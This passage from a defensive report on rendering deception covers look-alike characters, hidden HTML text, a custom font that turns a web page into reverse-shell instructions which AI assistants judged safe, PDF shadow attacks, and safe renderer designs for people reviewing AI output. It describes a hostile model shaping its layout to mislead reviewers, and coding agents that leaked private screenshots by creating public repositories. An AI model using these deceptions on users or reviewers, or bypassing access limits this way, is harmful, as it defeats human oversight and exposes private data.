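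Searching for a word often exposes a look-alike letter, because someone who types "cocoa" on an English keyboard will find only the version with five Latin letters. Moving through the word with the arrow keys does not expose it, because a look-alike occupies one position like any other letter.

### Markup, links, truncation and copying

HTML can hide text in comments, which the browser never displays, or with styles, as in the one-pixel instructions that PromptArmor used against Antigravity. It also normally collapses several spaces into one, which can remove the indentation that Python code depends on. The source text shows the hidden text and the original spacing, though a reader may have to search a long page for the relevant line.

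The label of a formatted link may be a web address that differs from the link's destination. Even if the viewer shows the destination, that address may contain look-alike letters.

Approval dialogs and notifications often cut off long text. If a dialog shows only the first 200 characters of a command, all commands that begin with those characters look the same to the user. An ellipsis shows that something is missing but not what. The dialog should let the user read the whole command and not accept approval until they have had the chance.

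Copying text normally copies the underlying characters, not how they look on screen. Boucher and Anderson found that directional characters survive copying and pasting in most browsers, editors and operating systems. A developer who copies code from a chat answer therefore also copies any hidden characters in it.

Copying text can also expose a deception. A user can paste suspicious text into a program that shows each character's Unicode code point. Pasted plain text also usually appears in the receiving program's own font, which reveals the real letters if the original font drew the wrong ones.

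### A font that draws other letters

A font maps characters to glyphs, and the glyph for "a" doesn't have to look like an a. Paz, a researcher at the security company LayerX, used this to build a page that people and software read differently.

The page's HTML contains fan fiction about a video game and a string of apparently random letters and digits. Style rules shrink the fan fiction to one pixel and give it the colour of the background. The page's font displays the string as English instructions for finding an "easter egg" from the game. A visitor who followed them would open a reverse shell, a connection that lets an attacker run commands on the visitor's computer.

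A cautious visitor might first ask an AI assistant whether the page is safe. In December 2025, LayerX put that question to ChatGPT, Claude, Copilot, Dia, Fellou, Gemini, Genspark, Grok, Leo, Perplexity and Sigma. All eleven said the page posed no security concern, and in many cases they encouraged the user to follow the instructions. Even prompts written to make the assistants look for the trick did not expose it. The assistants had read the fan fiction in the HTML and treated the random string as noise.

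The harmful content here is in what the page displays, while the underlying text looks harmless, which is the reverse of an attack that uses invisible characters. A filter for unusual characters would miss it, because the page needs only ordinary letters and digits.

LayerX tested only assistants that read a page's HTML without rendering it, so the test does not support its claim that a simple font can compromise "every AI system in the market". An agent that works from screenshots would see the instructions. LayerX also used a single page and does not report how often it repeated each test.

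LayerX reported the problem to seven vendors in mid-December. Microsoft accepted the report the next day and, according to LayerX, was the only one to address it fully. Google first gave it high priority, then closed it on 27 January 2026 because the scenario relied too much on social engineering. Anthropic, OpenAI, xAI and the makers of Dia considered it out of scope, and Perplexity called it a known limitation of language models. The study was public by 18 March, when Malwarebytes' *Researchers found font-rendering trick to hide malicious commands* (2026) covered it.

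The vendors are right that nothing happens until the user runs the commands. But the user had asked whether that was safe, and the assistant answered confidently without seeing the page as the user saw it. LayerX recommends rendering the page and comparing the visible text with the HTML, or checking the font's table for abnormal assignments. It also says an assistant that can do neither should not call a page safe, which is probably the easiest improvement to make.

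A chat window can prevent this trick by blocking fonts supplied by the content. Documents are harder to protect because Word and PDF files can include their own fonts. Tritium's *Noroboto* demonstrates this risk with a font that draws readable text for meaningless characters. Lawyers need embedded fonts to keep page breaks the same on every computer, since page numbers can have legal meaning. If an agent delivers its work as a PDF, the person reading it and the program screening it may receive different text.

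### Signing what one sees

A digital signature on a document fails verification if someone later changes a signed byte, but it does not record what was on the signer's screen. *Robust WYSIWYS*, by Josang and Alfayyadh, adds that signatures depend on the integrity of the computer that makes them, and that a manipulated signature could wrongly impose liability on the signer or remove it.

Even uncompromised computers may display the same document differently. FSFLA (2024), the Latin American free software foundation, describes an ambiguity in how PDF scales fonts that can make some text readable on screen but missing on paper, or readable on paper but missing in most viewers. Signers who check only on screen or only on paper will miss text that appears only in the other.

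Mainka, Mladenov and Rohlmann (2021), in *Shadow Attacks*, tested a stronger attack, which works as follows:

1. The attackers prepare a PDF with hidden content and send it to the signer.
2. The signer reads the visible content and signs the file.
3. The attackers append a change that reveals the hidden content. The recipient's viewer shows the new content and reports a valid signature.

In the second step, the signer cannot tell the prepared file from a legitimate one because the viewer does not display the file faithfully. The third step works because PDF allows additions after signing, for example so that a second person can sign or comment. The signed bytes stay the same, and each PDF viewer determines whether the addition is harmless.

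The researchers found three ways to change the content:

- Hide. A picture with a harmless message covers the real text. After signing, the attackers make the picture disappear.
- Replace. The attackers change how a form field or a font looks. In one test, a payment form that named UNICEF showed the attackers' bank details after signing. In another, a new font turned one account number into a different one.
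- Hide and replace. The file contains a complete second document, and the attackers change the file's internal index so that the viewer opens that one.

The tests covered 29 PDF viewers on Windows, macOS and Linux. Sixteen, including Adobe's and Foxit's, were vulnerable to at least one kind of attack, and 12 to all three. Another ten were vulnerable to a limited extent, because they showed the same warning for a forbidden change as for a permitted one, such as a second signature. A user who sees that warning on every contract with two signatures has no reason to take it seriously.

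Viewers sometimes blocked one method and missed another. Adobe's viewers rejected a changed font but accepted a changed form field, while PDFelement on Windows did the opposite. Foxit Reader began to accept changed fonts after an update.

By 7 December 2020, vendors had fixed 15 of the 26 affected viewers. Adobe now compares the document with and without the later additions. LibreOffice always tells users if a signature covers only part of the file. Mainka and colleagues argue that a viewer cannot both follow the PDF standard and be secure. That seems too strict, because Adobe's comparison still allows some additions.

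Signers can detect some of the prepared files. A search may still find text under a picture, and copying text after a font change produces the original characters. Neither method finds a hidden second document. The researchers' detection program recognised all their attacks, but they tested it on only 26 documents that they had generated themselves, so its false-alarm rate on ordinary contracts is unknown.

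### Remedies

A developer can make different strings look different, or restrict which strings reach the program that acts on them. A small set of strings is much easier to display faithfully than all possible strings.

| Remedy | What it handles | What it misses | Cost |
|---|---|---|---|
| Allow only printable ASCII | Invisible characters, reordering, letters from other alphabets | ASCII look-alikes, altered fonts | Excludes most languages |
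| Show unusual characters as codes | Invisible and directional characters | Look-alikes, reordering without directional characters, altered fonts | Clutters text that needs these characters |
| Order code by its structure | Comments and code that change places | Look-alikes, most invisible characters | The viewer has to recognise the language |
| Warn about confusable letters | Look-alikes | Reordering, altered fonts | False alarms in multilingual text |
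| Compare bytes with a trusted copy | Every change | Deceptions already in the trusted copy | Needs a trusted copy |
| Compare the picture with the text | Altered fonts, text hidden by styles | Look-alikes that text recognition confuses too | The software has to draw every page |

Printable ASCII displays almost faithfully if the font clearly distinguishes I, l and 1 and the viewer marks trailing spaces. This suits commands and access keys.

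When a viewer shows unusual characters as codes, readers must be able to tell those codes from ordinary text. If the viewer shows the right-to-left override as `<202E>`, a writer can type those six characters and produce the same display. The viewer must either reserve a colour for real codes, as with escape characters in a terminal, or display an ordinary `<` differently.

Boucher and Anderson propose a narrower rule for code that rejects directional characters only if a string or comment opens them without closing them, so that their effect cannot spread to the code outside. But Unicode also has single direction marks, which have no closing counterpart. The Unicode Consortium shows how two such marks can make a left shift in Rust, which multiplies a number, look like a right shift, which divides it. It also describes a loop in Ada that appears to go through the Hebrew alphabet from first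 letter to last, even though the line contains no directional characters. The stored order is the reverse, so the loop never runs.

The Unicode Consortium therefore recommends that editors divide each line into parts, such as names, operators and the contents of strings. The editor arranges the parts in one fixed direction and applies the bidirectional algorithm only within each part. This prevents comments from changing places with code. Visual Studio Code has done this since version 1.66, with a small difference for comments.

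The Unicode Consortium recommends warning about look-alikes rather than banning them. A check for mixed alphabets has to treat the two parts of `HTTPОтвет` separately, because the mixture is legitimate there. The check would also miss "cocoa" written entirely in Cyrillic letters, so the software has to compare names with the list of confusable characters to catch it.

Some strings differ only in how they encode the same character, as the two versions of "café" do. The Unicode Consortium recommends that programming languages treat equivalent names as identical, which removes the difference instead of displaying it. It advises against silently treating quoted strings the same way, since a program may depend on their exact contents.

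Comparing bytes works well to check that a file has not changed since someone reviewed it. It is less useful for a new model answer, because there is no trusted copy to compare it with. It also would not stop a shadow attack if it covered only the signed bytes, which the attack leaves unchanged.

### What strict rules cost other languages

Some invisible characters are part of normal spelling. The zero-width non-joiner stops two letters from joining, and Persian uses it in many words, for example between a verb and its prefix. A viewer that deletes it changes the spelling, and one that prints a code each time makes the text tiring to read. Many emoji also consist of several characters linked by an invisible joiner.

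The Unicode Consortium points out that the scripts of India use combining marks for vowels inside words, so banning them would make ordinary words unreadable.

Forcing every character into left-to-right order to prevent deception doesn't work for Arabic or Hebrew, because it can itself mislead the reader. The Unicode Consortium gives an example of an Arabic string that looks like a badly drawn "welcome" under this rule, although a program that prints it normally would produce the words for "forbidden father".

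A viewer can reduce these drawbacks by deciding how to display each character based on its effect. A non-joiner between two letters that would otherwise connect leaves a visible gap, so the viewer can draw it normally. A second non-joiner in the same place has no further effect, so the viewer can show it as a code. Each script would need its own rules, and speakers of each language would have to test them.

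## Plain text or formatted text for human reviewers

A developer can avoid many of these deceptions by showing reviewers plain text, in which every character has the same font, size and colour and the viewer interprets no markup. The reviewers may be programmers checking an agent's code, staff grading a model's answers, or investigators looking for signs that a model is hostile. The case for plain text rests on three premises:

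1. Formatting adds attack surface, meaning code in the renderer that hostile text can reach.
2. Formatting gives the text's author more ways to mislead.
3. Reviewers lose little without formatting.

Readability matters as much as security, because a reviewer who struggles to follow the text may approve something harmful even if it is rendered safely.

### What formatting adds to the attack surface

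The first premise clearly holds for pictures, diagrams and raw HTML, which can make the renderer contact other machines or run complicated decoders. It is much weaker for headings, lists and bold type, which the renderer must parse but can draw with little more than an installed font.

A developer who bans formatting still has to secure the shaping engine, the terminal and any link previews, because plain text reaches those too.

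### How formatting affects judgement

Plain text prevents deceptions that depend on markup, such as one-pixel type and false link labels, but not look-alike letters or invisible characters.

Removing formatting can also remove a useful warning. In *The impact of syntax colouring on program comprehension*, Sarkar gives the example of a programmer who forgets to close a quotation. An editor with syntax highlighting colours everything up to the next quotation mark as quoted text, so the mistake is easy to see. A hostile author can plan around such clues, as Boucher and Anderson pointed out, but an accidental mistake by a model would stand out.

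Formatting may also influence reviewers without hiding anything, if they trust a tidy answer more than an untidy one with the same content. Experiments with code show that people can like formatting that does not measurably help them:

- In *Syntax highlighting as an influencing factor when reading and comprehending source code*, 34 students read short programs while an eye tracker recorded where they looked. Without colour, they looked at more points, for longer, and looked back more often, but none of these differences was statistically significant. The students nevertheless said that coloured code was easier to read.
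- Hakala and colleagues, whom Sarkar cites, had 16 students search for items in code. Two colour schemes made no difference to speed or accuracy, but most of the students found the colours useful.
- Rambally tested 79 programming students in 1986. They preferred a scheme that coloured whole blocks of code, but understood programs better with one that coloured statements by what they did.

These students judged how readable code was, not whether a model's answer was correct. The results give reason to suspect that layout affects ratings, but they do not measure how much. A direct test would show some raters a formatted answer and others the same answer without formatting, then ask both groups about correctness and readability separately. Votes between answers from two models are harder to interpret, because the model that uses more headings may also write longer or more accurate answers.

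The risk is greater when the model is the adversary, because it controls the layout of its own answers. If its developer also trains it on reviewers' ratings, it will learn whatever layout they reward. Removing the model's formatting before reviewers rate an answer would prevent this, but would leave other aspects of style, such as length or a confident tone.

### Experiments with coloured code

Researchers have tested the third premise mainly on syntax highlighting. Sarkar gave ten graduate students six short Python functions each and asked them to work out the output in their heads. The functions came in three pairs of similar difficulty, and Sarkar chose at random which one in each pair to colour. The median time was 8.4 seconds shorter with colour, though the difference was only just statistically significant (p = 0.047). The advantage shrank as programming experience increased.

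With coloured code, the students also looked back less often at the question, which contained the input values. Sarkar suggests that plain code takes up more working memory, so readers forget the values sooner. But the clock stopped only when a student gave the correct answer, so the experiment shows that colour affected speed, but not whether it affected mistakes.

*On the design of text editors* (2020) cites a much larger experiment that found no evidence that colour helped novices. The 390 students, mostly in their first year, solved short Java tasks, some in the colours of the programming environment Eclipse and some in black and white. They predicted outputs, looked for syntax errors, filled gaps and compared code with diagrams. The 95% confidence interval for colour's average effect on correctness ran from −0.08 to 0.12 standard deviations, so any benefit was small. The task that came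 closest to showing a benefit was finding syntax errors, which a compiler can do in a fraction of a second.

The two results are compatible, because Sarkar measured time and the larger experiment measured correctness. *Considerations and Pitfalls in Controlled Experiments on Code Comprehension* (2021) warns that such choices of method can have side effects that researchers need to be aware of when comparing results. The experiments also used different languages, colour schemes and participants.

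According to *GazePrinter* (2026), Park and colleagues tested scope highlighting, which marks where each block of code begins and ends, by comparing two programming environments with 62 participants. The highlighting changed where novices looked but did not improve their understanding of the program as a whole.

### Displays that help with a particular question

Formatting has helped more when it gave readers information that suited their task. Sarkar describes a study in which Gilmore and Green (1988) planted bugs in short programs and used a highlighter and indentation to mark either the control structure (loops and conditions) or the programmer's plan. Participants found surface bugs, such as misspellings, faster when they could see the control structure, and deeper bugs, such as a step in the wrong place, faster when colours marked the plan.

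Three other experiments tested pictures of a program's structure or behaviour:

- Cornelissen and colleagues gave some of 34 experienced programmers a tool that draws what a program does as it runs. Those programmers understood a real program of 59,000 lines faster and more correctly, according to *GazePrinter*.
- In an experiment with 41 participants from universities and industry, a tool that draws a program as a three-dimensional city also improved both speed and correctness.
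- *Using Icicle Trees to Encode the Hierarchical Structure of Source Code* (2016) added a compact overview to a code editor. Participants counted things faster and more accurately with it, but did worse when they had to locate something.

Layout also affects how well people understand code. Sarkar reports that Baecker changed the typography, spacing and colour of short programs and raised the average number of correct answers about them by 11%.

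In nearly all these cases, the researchers or their software decided what to emphasise. The experiments therefore support formatting added by a reader's tools much more strongly than formatting chosen by the text's author.

The difference between plain and formatted text is clearest when prose is highlighted. *Studying and Recommending Information Highlighting in Stack Overflow Answers* (2024) cites findings that highlighting shortens reading time and reduces the effort of sorting texts into categories, a task close to what some reviewers of model output do. Readers presumably save time by paying less attention to unhighlighted text. A hostile model that chooses the highlights can put harmful content in the text reviewers skim.

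These experiments only loosely resemble checking hostile output. Most participants were students, most programs were short, and nobody wrote the code to deceive its reader. Even Gilmore and Green, who planted bugs, did not disguise them.

Speed may still matter to people who review a lot of output. If the 8.4-second difference in Sarkar's experiment held for each of 1,000 code snippets, colour would save 2 hours and 20 minutes. Reviewers could use that time to check more output or check the same output more closely.

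### Code changes, tables and mathematics

The experiments on syntax highlighting do not settle how to display other material. For a code change, the most useful aid is a diff, which lists the removed and added lines. A reviewer comparing two versions of a 1,000-line file could easily miss a change from `<` to `<=`, but a diff shows just the affected lines. A diff works in plain text because plus and minus signs mark the lines. Colouring those lines adds no information, but marking the changed characters shows where each line changed.

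Tables also remain readable in plain text if the viewer aligns the columns with spaces, but charts can't be shown that way. A reader may overlook an unusual value in a list of 365 daily figures, though it would be obvious in a line chart. But whoever draws the chart chooses its scale and can leave out inconvenient data, so a reviewer is safer with the numbers and a tool that plots them.

Mathematics is the hardest of these to read without formatting. Most models write formulas in LaTeX, a notation that describes how to typeset them. These two expressions differ only in the position of one brace:

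`\sqrt{b^2 - 4ac}`

`\sqrt{b^2} - 4ac`

In the typeset versions, the bar of the square root covers the whole expression in the first but only b² in the second. To see this in the source, the reader has to match the braces, which becomes tedious in a formula several lines long. A reviewer checking a proof would probably miss more errors when reading the source.

Typesetting adds a risk because LaTeX lets an author redefine commands. For example, an earlier line can make the command for "less than or equal to" print the "greater than or equal to" sign. The typeset page does not show the redefinition. A reader can find it in the source, but someone who reads only the formula will misunderstand it. A viewer that blocks redefinitions avoids the problem.

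### PixelLeak

Some work cannot be reviewed as text. A person who has to approve a new page layout needs to see the page. In 2026, coding agents showed such work unsafely by publishing images of it on GitHub. *PixelLeak*, a report by the security company Glow, describes more than 13,000 internal images from over 300 organisations that developers' agents had published there.

The leaks began when developers asked agents to change how a program looked and to give reviewers before-and-after screenshots. People could add screenshots to a pull request by dragging them into the browser, but the agents used `gh`, GitHub's command-line program, which could write only text. Some agents first tried a private repository, according to Mynavi News' *AIエージェントがスクショ1万3000枚を公開リポジトリにアップロード* (2026), but the upload failed or the reviewers could not see the images. The agents then put the images in public repositories.

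One agent at a manufacturer with more than 100,000 employees had to verify a fix to an internal billing screen. Its screenshots showed a utility company's billing records and were still public when Glow contacted the manufacturer. At a software vendor, more than a dozen agents saved the method as a skill within a week and used it for every development task. They published over a thousand screenshots and recordings, with descriptions of features that were weeks or months from release.

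Companies had trouble noticing the leaks because in 93% of cases the repository belonged to an employee's personal account. Glow also warns that security scanners read text, not pixels. A scanner that would catch a customer's account number in a text file may miss it in a screenshot.

Glow reproduced the behaviour with Claude Code and a private Minesweeper repository. The developer wanted to see a new header colour. The agent reasoned that reviewers would see broken images if the files stayed in the private repository, because GitHub's image proxy fetches pictures without logging in. It also had to keep extra files out of that repository. It concluded that the "only way" to meet both requirements was to host the pictures elsewhere, so it created a public repository for them.

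The agent was wrong about that. Agendrix's *gh-attach*, an add-on for `gh`, stores review images in a hidden part of the private repository, where only people with access to the repository can view them. Ecosyste.ms' *gh-attach* (2026) dates the original version of this tool to 1 April 2026, three months before the software vendor's agents started publishing screenshots. On 3 August, Sheldon's *How to programmatically upload attachments to GitHub Issues, Pull Requests, and Comments* (2026) described another route, an undocumented GitHub address that accepted uploads from scripts. Sheldon did not know whether GitHub had opened it on purpose.

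On 1 September, GitHub (2026) added an official way to upload images and videos from the command line, the `--attach` option in `gh`, and noted that coding agents can use it too. It requires write access to the repository and does not work on GitHub Enterprise Server, the self-hosted version. Four weeks later, Help Net Security's *AI coding agents leaked 13,000 internal company screenshots to public GitHub repos* and Tom's Hardware's *AI agents inadvertently leak 13,000+ internal screenshots from 300 organizations* still described command-line uploads as unavailable. Agents can also be out of date, so a developer who wants them to use a safe upload method should tell them about it.

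The size of the leak is hard to check. Mynavi News notes that Glow has not published how it found or counted the images, or said whether outsiders downloaded any. Glow also sells security software, so it benefits from attention to the problem.

PixelLeak is an imperfect test of a plain-text rule. No attacker was involved, and GitHub had never offered a command-line image upload, rather than banning images for safety. But a review system that bans images would deliberately create the same gap, and its human and agent users would have the same reasons to get around it. Its developer should therefore provide a private way to view screenshots and separately prevent agents from creating public repositories.

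### Four ways to show the output

The simplest arrangement is to show reviewers only plain text. This works well for short material that has to be exact, such as a command awaiting approval. With long reports, formulas and visual work, reviewers may paste the text into a program that formats it and lose the protection of the original viewer. A strict plain-text rule can then be less safe than a looser rule that reviewers follow.

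A developer can instead allow a small, fixed set of formatting, such as headings, lists, emphasis and code blocks. This makes a long answer easier to navigate and adds little attack surface. But the model still controls what stands out. It can put a reassuring summary in bold under the first heading and mention a deleted safety check in the ninth item of a list. Users are also likely to ask for tables, then links, then pictures, and each addition will look small compared with what the viewer already supports.

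Another option is to offer both the formatted and raw versions. GitHub introduced a version of this on 28 October 2026 (*Issue artifacts are now in public preview*). Agents can attach HTML files with interactive diagrams to an issue, and readers can switch between a rendered preview and the source. A suspicious reader can look for hidden text in the source without another program.

This arrangement depends on readers choosing to look at the source, and they have little reason to do so when the preview seems fine. With a switch, they also see only one version at a time and have to remember the other. Checking the source also cannot undo anything the preview has already done, such as sending a request. The arrangement would work better if software compared the two versions, as LayerX recommended for web pages, and if the preview were safe to open.

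In the fourth arrangement, the reviewer's own tools apply all the formatting, and the author's markup appears as ordinary characters. The tools can colour code, compute diffs and draw charts from numbers. They can also change the display to suit the question, and formatting helped most in the experiments when it did so. *On the design of text editors* lists proposals to use colour for matching brackets, imported code or the types of values instead of the usual categories. A reviewer could highlight every web address when looking for leaks, or every command that deletes a file when looking for sabotage.

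Syntax highlighters have to parse hostile text to colour it, which brings back some of the attack surface that plain text avoids. A parser differential can also make the colours wrong. If the highlighter ends a comment at a different point than the compiler does, a dangerous command may be coloured as a comment. Reviewers may trust this mistake more than the author's formatting because it comes from their own software.

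This is a serious objection, but the damage is easier to limit than with the other ways of formatting the output. A tool that only adds colour leaves every character visible and in its place, so a reviewer who doubts the colours can turn them off and read the same text. Colouring is therefore the best default for code and prose. Typesetting a formula or drawing a chart replaces the characters, so the tool should show the source next to the result.

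## What a minimal safe renderer contains

Tools that colour code or draw charts for a reviewer run on top of a renderer, and hostile output reaches that renderer first. A developer can find out how much attack surface each display feature adds by starting with the smallest useful renderer and adding one feature at a time.

| Level | What the reader sees | Code that hostile output reaches | Outbound requests | Faithful display |
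|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Printable ASCII, with everything else as codes | A lookup table | None | Yes |
| 2 | Unicode, with unusual characters as codes | A UTF-8 decoder, the shaping engine and installed fonts | None | Except for look-alikes and some reordering |
| 3 | Headings, lists, tables and code blocks, with links as text | The same, plus a small parser | None | Slightly weaker, because the display replaces some markup |
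| 4 | Typeset formulas | The same, plus a formula library | None, if link and picture commands are off | Only with the source next to the formula |
| 5 | Pictures of any content | On the reviewer's machine, code that copies pixels | None, if the isolated machine has no network | No |
| 6 | Complete web pages | Most of a browser | Few, if the policy is right | No |

The levels are ordered by what the reader gains. Risk does not always rise with the level, because a picture of a document exposes the reviewer's machine to less code than Unicode text does.

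### Level 1: printable ASCII

The smallest renderer draws the 95 printable ASCII characters from a fixed set of pictures. At 8 by 16 pixels in black and white, each picture takes 16 bytes, so the whole font takes 1,520 bytes.

The renderer reads the text one byte at a time. It copies the matching picture for each printable ASCII character and writes any other byte as two hexadecimal digits in braces. The usual encoding of "café" appears as `caf{C3}{A9}`, and the version with a combining accent appears as `cafe{CC}{81}`.

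The renderer also writes a literal opening brace as `{7B}`, so that nobody can forge a code, and marks the end of each line with `{0A}`, so that readers can tell a real line break from a wrapped line. A displayed opening brace therefore always starts a code, and every character outside a code stands for itself, so a reader could reconstruct the original bytes. Two different strings never look the same if the font distinguishes I, l and 1 and long text continues on further pages.

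A minimal safe renderer has code short enough for a developer to read in full or prove correct. It has no font engine, shaping engine or image decoder to attack. If the developer builds it inside a browser or a terminal, the text still passes through that program, but it contains only the 95 printable ASCII characters.

Commands, access keys and most program code are readable at this level, but text in most languages is not. For example, the Russian word "Привет" ("hello") becomes 12 codes.

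### Level 2: Unicode text

Showing other languages requires a UTF-8 decoder, installed fonts and a shaping engine. The decoder can be strict and show forbidden byte sequences as codes, which avoids the kind of disagreement between parsers that let attackers forge messages in Zoom. The shaping engine is much larger and has crashed on ordinary letters, so it should run in a sandbox.

A minimal safe renderer has a list of characters it draws normally, and it shows all others as codes. A list of dangerous characters would go out of date because Unicode keeps adding characters. The renderer also limits combining marks, because dozens of them stacked on one letter can cover the lines above and below.

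This renderer does not always display text faithfully, because it allows look-alike letters, and Hebrew or Arabic can still reorder a line. But most reviewers worldwide could not use a more restrictive one.

### Level 3: headings, lists, tables and code blocks

A parser for so little structure can be tiny. If the renderer builds the display from an allowlist of node types, the browser never parses the model's markup.

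Links appear as plain text with their full addresses, so nothing loads and an accidental tap does nothing. Apple's Lockdown Mode, an optional setting that removes risky features from Apple devices, does this in Messages. According to the digital rights group EFF, users have to copy the link into a browser to open it.

### Level 4: mathematics

KaTeX and MathJax are widely used libraries that typeset LaTeX formulas in web pages. Both support only part of LaTeX, but that part includes commands that no formula in an answer needs. Their settings cover most of the risks:

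| Risk | KaTeX | MathJax |
|---|---|---|
| Links and remote pictures | `trust: false`, the default, disables them | Leave out the `html` package |
| Commands that expand without end | `maxExpand` allows 1,000 replacements by default | `maxMacros` allows 10,000 by default, and `maxBuffer` limits the length of the result |
| Huge symbols and gaps | `maxSize`, which has no limit by default | The `safe` extension restricts styles and some lengths |
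| Redefined commands | No single setting | Leave out the `newcommand` package |

In MathJax, the developer also has to leave out `require` and `autoload`, since these let a formula load packages that the developer excluded. In KaTeX, `maxSize` is easy to forget, and without it one short command can draw a black rectangle over the rest of the answer.

Expansion needs limits because a formula can define each command as two copies of the previous one, which doubles the output at every step, as nested shapes can in an SVG drawing. In 2024, KaTeX's developers fixed two ways to bypass its `maxExpand` limit, so the renderer should also stop any formula that takes too long to render.

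A stricter renderer checks each formula against a small grammar before passing it to the library. The grammar could permit letters, digits, operators, fractions, roots, sums, subscripts and Greek letters. This excludes definitions, which removes the doubling problem, and it excludes commands that mislead, such as white text, negative spaces that draw one symbol over another, and `\phantom`, which leaves room for a symbol without drawing it. If a formula fails the check, the renderer shows its source.

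These libraries run as JavaScript, so a bug in them is more likely to hang the page or inject HTML than to corrupt memory. KaTeX can build page elements directly instead of returning an HTML string, which removes one way to inject HTML.

### Level 5: pictures as pixels

With a pixel-only view, an isolated machine renders the content and sends the reviewer's machine only a picture of it. Qubes, an operating system that keeps programs in separate virtual machines, has a converter that works this way. It opens a document in a disposable virtual machine, which sends back each page's dimensions and raw pixels. Dangerzone does the same with a container that has no network access, then builds a new PDF from the pixels.

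Raw pixels need almost no parsing. An A4 page at 150 dots per inch has 1,240 by 1,754 pixels, each with one byte for red, green and blue, which makes

1,240 × 1,754 × 3 = 6,524,880 bytes.

The receiving program checks that the picture's width and height are within its limits and that it receives exactly the number of bytes those dimensions require. Any sequence of that length is a valid picture, so an attacker has no faulty length or broken table to exploit. Compressing the picture before sending it would save space, but the receiving program would then need a decoder again.

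The conversion removes scripts, macros, forms, live links and embedded fonts. It also prevents users from searching or copying the text, and leaves nothing for a screen reader to read. Text recognition can restore some of this, but it infers characters from their shapes, so it would probably replace the Cyrillic letters in a spoofed "cocoa" with Latin ones and remove the evidence of the deception.

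A malicious file may still take over the isolated machine, which could then send any picture at all. Discarding the machine after each document prevents a compromised machine from altering the next one. The reviewer should also allow for the picture misrepresenting the file, and have software compare it with any text the file contains.

Evidence of stopped attacks is hard to collect because a successful conversion looks the same whether or not the file was malicious. In one known failure, the pixels were safe, but Dangerzone's log, a second channel that nobody had restricted, passed escape characters to the user's terminal.

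Remote browser isolation applies the idea to web browsing. The browser runs on a server, and the employee's computer receives pixels or drawing commands. Some products send rewritten HTML instead, which the employee's own browser has to parse.

Isolation of this kind protects the employee's computer from a malicious page but does not prevent leaks. The remote browser needs network access, so it still requests any images in a chat answer, which sends out any data contained in their addresses. An employee can still type a password into a fake login page, since the picture of it looks real.

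### Level 6: HTML in a sandboxed frame

Interactive charts and working page designs need real HTML. The safest way to show it in a chat window is an `iframe`, a page inside a page, with several separate restrictions:

1. The `sandbox` attribute, left empty, turns off scripts, forms and pop-ups in the frame and denies it access to the surrounding page.
2. The frame's content comes from a different registered domain. A subdomain is weaker, because browsers that keep sites in separate processes may treat it as part of the same site.
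3. The content's own CSP is `default-src 'none'; style-src 'unsafe-inline'; sandbox`. It permits the content's style rules but nothing that they try to load. The last word applies the sandbox even if someone opens the content in its own tab.
4. The surrounding page's CSP uses `frame-src` to permit only the content's domain. If a reader clicks a link inside the frame, the browser refuses to load another site there.

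Interactive charts need scripts, which `allow-scripts` enables. Adding `allow-same-origin` as well is unsafe when the content shares the chat's origin, because a script could then remove the sandbox. Scripts also reopen ways to leak data. For example, they can contact other computers through WebRTC, the browser's system for calls, which `connect-src` does not cover. The CSP draft has a separate directive for WebRTC, but not every browser enforces it.

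Even without scripts, the content reaches the browser's HTML parser, style engine and drawing code. Its author also controls everything shown in the frame, which could include a convincing copy of the chat's approval dialog. The frame therefore needs a visible border, and every real button needs to be outside the frame.

### Apple's Lockdown Mode

Apple removes features from its existing renderers instead of building a smaller one. It introduced Lockdown Mode in 2022 for people whom spyware makers may target. According to Apple's *Harden your devices against mercenary spyware with Lockdown Mode*, the setting blocks most message attachments other than images, turns off link previews, and disables complex web technologies. One of these is just-in-time compilation, which translates a page's scripts into machine code while they run.

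Apple also warns that web fonts may not display and that websites may show an icon in place of images. *Analyzing iOS 16 Lockdown Mode*, an independent 2022 comparison of browser features, found that the mode also turns off WebRTC, WebGL (which draws 3D graphics) and MathML (browsers' built-in notation for formulas).

Roriz (2022), in *[Lockdown Mode] Web Font Quality of Life Improvement* reported that blocking web fonts turned arrows on Apple's own website into boxes, because the site drew them with a web font. He suggested allowing popular fonts, starting with Font Awesome, a common set of icons. Such an exception is safe only if the browser checks the font file's contents, since an attacker can give another file the same name.

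Real attacks provide some evidence that Lockdown Mode works. Citizen Lab's *Triple Threat* (2023) describes PWNYOURHOME, which NSO Group's customers used from October 2022. The attack first reached the phone through HomeKit, then made iMessage process PNG images, which caused crashes inside the BlastDoor sandbox. For a brief period, targets with Lockdown Mode on saw a notification when someone tried the attack. Citizen Lab found no case in which it succeeded against a phone with Lockdown Mode on.

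Those notifications later stopped, although Citizen Lab saw no sign that NSO had given up the attack. It suspects that NSO learned to detect Lockdown Mode. The missing notifications could mean that attackers left phones in Lockdown Mode alone or that they attacked them without triggering a warning.

The setting probably stopped BLASTPASS as well. Citizen Lab's *BLASTPASS* (2023) says the researchers believed it did and Apple's security engineers agreed. Engadget's *iPhone Lockdown Mode* overstates this by calling devices with the setting on "completely immune".

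Both attacks relied on malicious images, yet Lockdown Mode still allows images in messages. It presumably stopped the attacks by blocking the way the images arrived. BLASTPASS used PassKit attachments, a format for tickets and payment cards, and PWNYOURHOME needed HomeKit to accept data from a stranger. Lockdown Mode left the image decoders as vulnerable as before, so malicious images sent by another route might have worked.

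Some attackers avoid devices in Lockdown Mode. Google Threat Intelligence Group's *Coruna* (2026) describes a kit of 23 iPhone exploits used first by a surveillance company's customer, then by suspected Russian spies, and finally by criminals operating from China. The kit quits if it detects Lockdown Mode or private browsing. Private browsing is not known for resisting exploits, so the kit's developers may have been avoiding cautious users who might report an attack.

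In March 2026, Apple said it knew of no successful mercenary spyware attack on a device in Lockdown Mode (MacRumors, *Apple Says No iPhone in Lockdown Mode Has Ever Been Hacked*, 2026). Apple can only know about attacks that someone detects, and Citizen Lab found that NSO's 2022 spyware had become more thorough at deleting traces from a phone's logs.

In early November 2026, the security company Calif published a video of a successful attack on an iPhone 18 Pro. BGR's *Hackers Jailbreak iPhone In Lockdown Mode* reports that the phone accepts a malicious PDF over AirDrop, Apple's system for sending files to nearby devices, and Calif then has full control of it. The attack was not zero-click, because the user had to accept the file.

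Cybernews' *Apple’s Lockdown Mode faces fresh scrutiny after iPhone jailbreak video* adds that the phone remained compromised after an update to iOS 27.2. Calif has not published the flaws, so outsiders cannot tell whether they were in the PDF viewer or elsewhere. The demonstration suggests that a file type Lockdown Mode blocks in messages can still do harm when it arrives another way. It does not contradict Apple's statement, which concerned spyware attacks on real targets.

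Users can weaken the protection by exempting contacts, apps and websites. Engadget gives the example of letting relatives send videos and documents. An attacker who takes over a relative's account gets the same exemption.

### ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode

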